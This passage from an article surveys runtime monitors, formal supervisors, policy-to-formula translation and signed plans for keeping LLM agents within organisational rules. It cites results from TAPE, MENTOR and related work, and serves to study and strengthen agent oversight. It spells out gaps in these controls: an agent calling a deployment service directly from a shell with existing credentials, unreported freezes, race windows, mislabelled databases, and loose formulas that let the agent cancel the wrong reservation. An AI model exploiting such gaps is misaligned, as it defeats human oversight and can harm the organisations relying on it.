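1. The model writes several plans, each with the states it expects to pass through. TAPE merges states that represent the same situation, which turns the plans into one graph.
2. The model estimates what each step will cost and how good each outcome is. An exact solver then picks the best path that stays within the budget.
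3. TAPE restricts the model's output so that it can only write the next call on that path.
4. After the call, TAPE compares the situation it has reached with the one the path predicted. If they match, it continues. If they differ, it has the model write new plans and solves the problem again with the remaining budget.

Suppose a household robot opens a cupboard that should contain a mug according to its plan, and the cupboard is empty. The real state doesn't match the predicted one, so TAPE replans from the open cupboard. Small differences in the wording of a tool's reply don't trigger a new plan, because the merged states record only facts such as the robot's location, what it is holding and its progress.

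Jeong and colleagues tested TAPE with GPT-4.1 mini on Sokoban, a puzzle in which the player pushes boxes onto targets and can get a box permanently stuck against a wall. They measured planning errors, in which the model chooses a move that makes the puzzle unsolvable, and sampling errors, in which it outputs a different move from the one it chose.

| Agent | Planning errors | Sampling errors | Puzzles solved |
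|---|---|---|---|
| Chooses one step at a time | 50.7% | 8.3% | 5% |
| Has a full plan as advice | 47.7% | 4.7% | 17% |
| TAPE | 36.7% | 0.0% | 46% |

TAPE solved 38% of the puzzles without replanning, and 36% with replanning but no restriction on the model's output. The standard errors are about 5 points, so neither result is conclusively different from the full system's 46%. Removing replanning, the restriction and the solver together reduced the rate to 11%. GPT-4.1 mini is an old model, but Jeong and colleagues also found a gain with the stronger GPT-5 nano.

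TAPE follows its path as strictly as SOTERIA's strict mode would, and these results suggest that strictness can help an agent finish when the software replans promptly. But TAPE checks only budgets, and it relies on the model's estimates of how much of the budget each step will use. The model also builds the graph, so it may treat two different situations as the same and miss a mismatch. To use TAPE for airline cancellations, a developer would have to remove the steps that break the airline's rules from each new graph before the solver chooses a path.

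## From the formal model to the deployed agent

TAPE's exact solver is only as reliable as the graph it works on. Every proof about a plan has a similar weakness, because it covers a model of the system, not the system itself. Gu and Zhu's net for the release agent has at most 32 reachable markings, but the deployed agent works with files, credentials, servers and people that the net mostly leaves out. A proof that the net never reaches "published during a freeze" protects the real release only if the net describes the system correctly.

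### How safety carries over from the net

In *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI*, Gu and Zhu state four assumptions under which a supervisor that is safe on the net also keeps the running system safe. A real state x is safe if no unauthorised action has taken place. A relation R links real states to markings, and (x, M) ∈ R means that M correctly describes x. The theorem needs all four assumptions. For each one, the last column of the table gives a failure that can occur when only that assumption is false.

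| Assumption | What it requires | What can happen without it |
|---|---|---|
| Correct start | The first marking describes the real starting state | The net starts with an approval that no person gave |
| Matching steps | After each real step, the updated marking describes the new real state | The interface reads a call that deletes the production database as one that deletes the test copy |
| Safety means safety | If a marking is not forbidden, the real states it describes are safe | Nobody listed a leaked credential as forbidden, so the supervisor doesn't prevent the leak |
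| No bypass, for actions | Every consequential action by the agent passes the admission check first | The agent calls the deployment service directly from a shell |
| No bypass, for events | The monitor learns of every outside event and updates the net | An incident freezes releases, but the monitor never hears of it and allows a release |

The proof is an induction on the number of real steps. It shows that after every step, the marking still describes the real state and is reachable in the supervised net.

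1. At the start, this holds by the first assumption.
2. By the fourth assumption, the next real step is a call that the monitor admitted, an event that the monitor recorded, or an internal step such as drafting text.
3. For a call or an event, the monitor fires the matching transition. The supervisor permits that transition, so the supervised net can reach the new marking. By the second assumption, the new marking describes the new real state. An internal step leaves the marking unchanged and still correct.
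4. The supervisor is safe on the net, so no marking reached in this way is forbidden. By the third assumption, every real state along the way is therefore safe.

The theorem does not guarantee that the agent can finish. Every step the real system takes has a counterpart in the net, but the net may also contain steps that the real system cannot take. For example, the net can have a path to "live" while the deployment service is down.

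### Bypasses, late reports and delays

Gu and Zhu call the fourth assumption *complete mediation*. The monitor cannot ensure it alone, because it checks only the calls that reach it. Engineers have to block the other routes by running the agent in a sandbox and giving the tools' credentials to a trusted broker. An agent that contacts the deployment service from a shell then has no credential to present. If the shell already has its own credentials, however, the agent can use them to reach the service, because the monitor checks only the call to the shell tool, which is permitted.

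A sandbox doesn't help with outside events. Tool results already come back through the monitor, and developers can make a human approval take effect only when the person enters it there. But an incident happens elsewhere, so its source has to report it over an authenticated channel. The monitor stops when an event doesn't fit the net, but this doesn't catch a late report, because the net still allows an incident at that point. Gu and Zhu therefore suggest that the monitor check with the source for a freeze just before admitting a release.

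Even then, a freeze could begin in the short time a network call takes, after the monitor's query but before the server publishes. This would violate the second assumption, which requires an admitted call and the update to the marking to take effect together, with no outside event in between. To prevent this, the deployment service would probably have to check for a freeze itself when it publishes. The monitor must also handle calls one at a time, because otherwise two agents could both find and use the same approval mark.

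Gu and Zhu consider the interface between calls and transitions the part most prone to error. Suppose the interface identifies the test database by name, and an administrator has pointed that name at the production server. When the agent asks to delete the test copy, the net records a harmless deletion and the company loses its production data, even though the proof contains no error.

### Turning a written policy into formulas

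The third assumption holds only if someone has written down everything that counts as harm. Most organisations have only a policy in prose, and translating it into a formal language is difficult. Dantas and colleagues call specification the bottleneck. They report that on one benchmark, only 24.8% to 34.2% of language models' translations into PDDL, a standard language for planning problems, had the right meaning. Their review covers studies from 2022 onwards, so this range may not apply to the best current models.

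Such translations are usually valid PDDL, so a syntax check accepts them. A mistranslated policy formula can pass a syntax check too. Suppose a model translates the airline's first rule as "every call to Cancel-Resv follows a call to No-Flown that returned true" and leaves out the requirement that both calls concern the same reservation. An agent could then call No-Flown on RES456, get true, and cancel RES123. The verifier would accept the plan, the monitor would allow the cancellation, and a score based on the same formula would show full conformance.

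He and colleagues rely on human review to catch such errors. A language model drafts the tool contracts and policy formulas from the policy document and from each tool's written description and input and output types. A person then checks the drafts and goes through the policy clause by clause. Every rule about changing data needs at least one formula if a trace of tool calls can show whether the agent obeyed the rule. This took a few hours for each benchmark, mostly spent reading the policy and checking the drafts. The airline benchmark needed 24 formulas, the shop benchmark 33 and Toolathlon 41.

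A few hours is little time to spend on rules that apply to every later task. But the review missed some errors, which He and colleagues found only when they audited their test results. A company would need to audit real runs in a similar way, and its manuals may well be longer and vaguer than a benchmark's policy.

MENTOR automates more of the review with three language-model agents:

1. A translator turns the manual into formulas.
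2. An evaluator invents example traces and labels each one as compliant or not according to the manual.
3. An ordinary program checks the formulas against the traces and reports every disagreement.
4. The translator corrects the formula or contests the label by pointing to the manual, and the evaluator reviews the objection. An orchestrator settles any remaining disputes.

The loop ends when the formulas agree with the labels or when it reaches a fixed number of rounds. Anand and colleagues say that agreement is some evidence that the translation is correct but doesn't prove it. The translator and the evaluator could misread an ambiguous clause in the same way, and the traces might not include the case where a formula fails.

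Results depended heavily on which model ran the loop. The table shows the percentage of IT operations tasks that three small agents passed in all three runs, using rules from four models.

| Agent | Rules by Claude Opus 5 | Rules by GPT-5.5 | Rules by Claude Sonnet | Rules by Qwen3.8 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 38% | 47% | 9% | 11% |
| Qwen3 8B | 64% | 68% | 34% | 34% |
| Gemma 4 E4B | 75% | 79% | 68% | 55% |

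No single model wrote the best rules in every case. Llama passed 28% of the shop tasks with rules from Opus 5 but only 9% with rules from GPT-5.5. It therefore seems sensible to test a new set of rules on the agent that will work under them, even if a strong model wrote them.

### Harms that the manual does not mention

Even a perfect translation leaves out any rule that the policy lacks. In *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026) give the example of an assistant that resolves calendar conflicts. When a user's appointment to treat a sexually transmitted disease overlaps with a work meeting, the assistant moves the meeting and reveals the reason in its email to the user's colleagues. No attacker is involved, and each of the assistant's tools works as intended.

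To find such cases in advance, Doshi and colleagues adapt a method of hazard analysis from aviation and other high-risk fields. Developers list the people whom the agent affects, what each of them values, and what loss would follow if the agent failed to respect it. They then work out which actions could cause that loss and write rules against them. For the calendar, this gives two rules:

- An email may not contain event details that are private to people other than the recipient, unless the user agrees.
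- After every change to an event, the agent must send one email to each attendee.

Doshi and colleagues tested the approach in Alloy, a tool that searches all runs of a model up to a chosen length. Alloy quickly found leaks in the model without the rules, but none once the rules were added. This result, too, is about a model, because they had not yet built the program that would enforce the rules on a real agent.

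### Tools that break their contracts

SOTERIA's contracts start from the tools' descriptions, so an outdated description can produce a false contract. The run-time check of postconditions catches this only if the error is visible in the tool's result.

Such a check would have missed the wrong patient registrations that Anand and colleagues found in SOP-Bench. The benchmark's registration tool ignores its inputs and returns the correct stored answer for each patient, so its output looks right even when the agent passes it the wrong details. MENTOR compared the inputs with the agent's earlier lookups before allowing a registration, and none of the successful runs with its text feedback had this fault.

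Tools from outside suppliers are harder to trust. Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard. According to Doshi and colleagues, the protocol offers developers only a few optional annotations and the advice to treat tools as untrusted. They propose requiring every tool to carry labels that state what it can do, whether its data is confidential, and whether its output is verified. A company can probably trust such labels on its own tools. For other tools, it would need vetted suppliers or independent certification, since the author of a malicious tool can label it "read-only".

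### A language model inside an exact check

MENTOR's verdicts follow fixed rules, but a language model, called the labelling model here, supplies some of the facts. Before the first call, it turns the user's request into a structured record, such as a trip from Toronto to Chicago, business class, not urgent. Whenever a tool returns free text, the model assigns at most one label from a short list, for example "500 km or more". Ordinary code makes every decision after that. But if the model wrongly records the trip as urgent, the code can apply the exception for urgent business and allow a booking that the manual forbids.

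Anand and colleagues tested different labelling models on the medical game. With GPT-4.1, the Qwen3 8B agent passed 80% of the tasks in all three runs, and with GPT-4.1 mini it passed 70%. With each of five open models that had no extra training, it passed between 2% and 7%. Strictly enforcing wrong labels was therefore much worse than enforcing nothing, since the same agent passed 33% without any monitor, even though that test required success in all five runs.

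A Qwen3 model with 4 billion parameters scored 68%, nearly as high as GPT-4.1 mini, after training mostly on labels from GPT-4.1. A company can therefore run its own small labelling model, although the training may pass on GPT-4.1's mistakes. On the shop tasks, the choice of labelling model made little difference, presumably because fewer decisions there depended on free text. If a tool can return a distance as a number, ordinary code can compare it with 500 without a labelling model.

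### A signed plan

If one organisation approves a plan and another carries out its actions, the second needs to know exactly what the first approved. Schrock (2026), in *Bounded Execution Programs for Consequential Agent Actions*, proposes a signed file for this purpose. The file contains a graph without cycles, of at most 256 nodes. Each node specifies

- an exact action or a defined class of actions;
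- which earlier nodes must have finished, and with what outcome;
- how many times the node may run;
- how much each attempt takes from shared budgets.

In one example, a plan lets an agent repair a production system once, and only after an inspection has succeeded. The plan is valid for an hour and allows three attempts in total.

The program that admits calls keeps one shared record of what has run. It deducts from the budget just before a request goes out and does not restore the amount if the connection drops. The outcome then counts as "indeterminate", which does not permit the agent to retry. The call also counts toward the plan's limit on simultaneous actions until someone establishes what happened.

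An agent cannot change a signed plan. To replan, it needs a new version with a new signature and a fresh authorisation, and the old version must have no reserved calls waiting to start. The new version's budgets start unused, much as a new SOTERIA plan starts with empty logs. The signer therefore has to subtract what the agent has already used from the new budgets, or require evidence of that use in the new plan.

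Schrock states that the signature does not show that the signer understood the plan, that the plan is safe, or that every action passes through the check. Operators who leave another credential or route open may not claim that the whole plan is enforced. Schrock's companion draft, *Bounded Capability Receipts and Durable Spend Control for Agent Actions* (2026), similarly requires, for spending limits, that all copies of the software that can spend from one budget share a single record. Otherwise the limit applies to each copy separately, and two copies could each spend the full amount.

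The plan format is an individual proposal, not a standard. Schrock published it in August 2026 as an Internet-Draft, a working document in the format of the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops internet standards. The draft expires in February 2027 unless a new version replaces it. The IETF's website lists the companion draft as "individual", with no publication stream assigned. Schrock's team has written a reference implementation of the plan format, but the draft reports no independent implementation and no lasting use in production.
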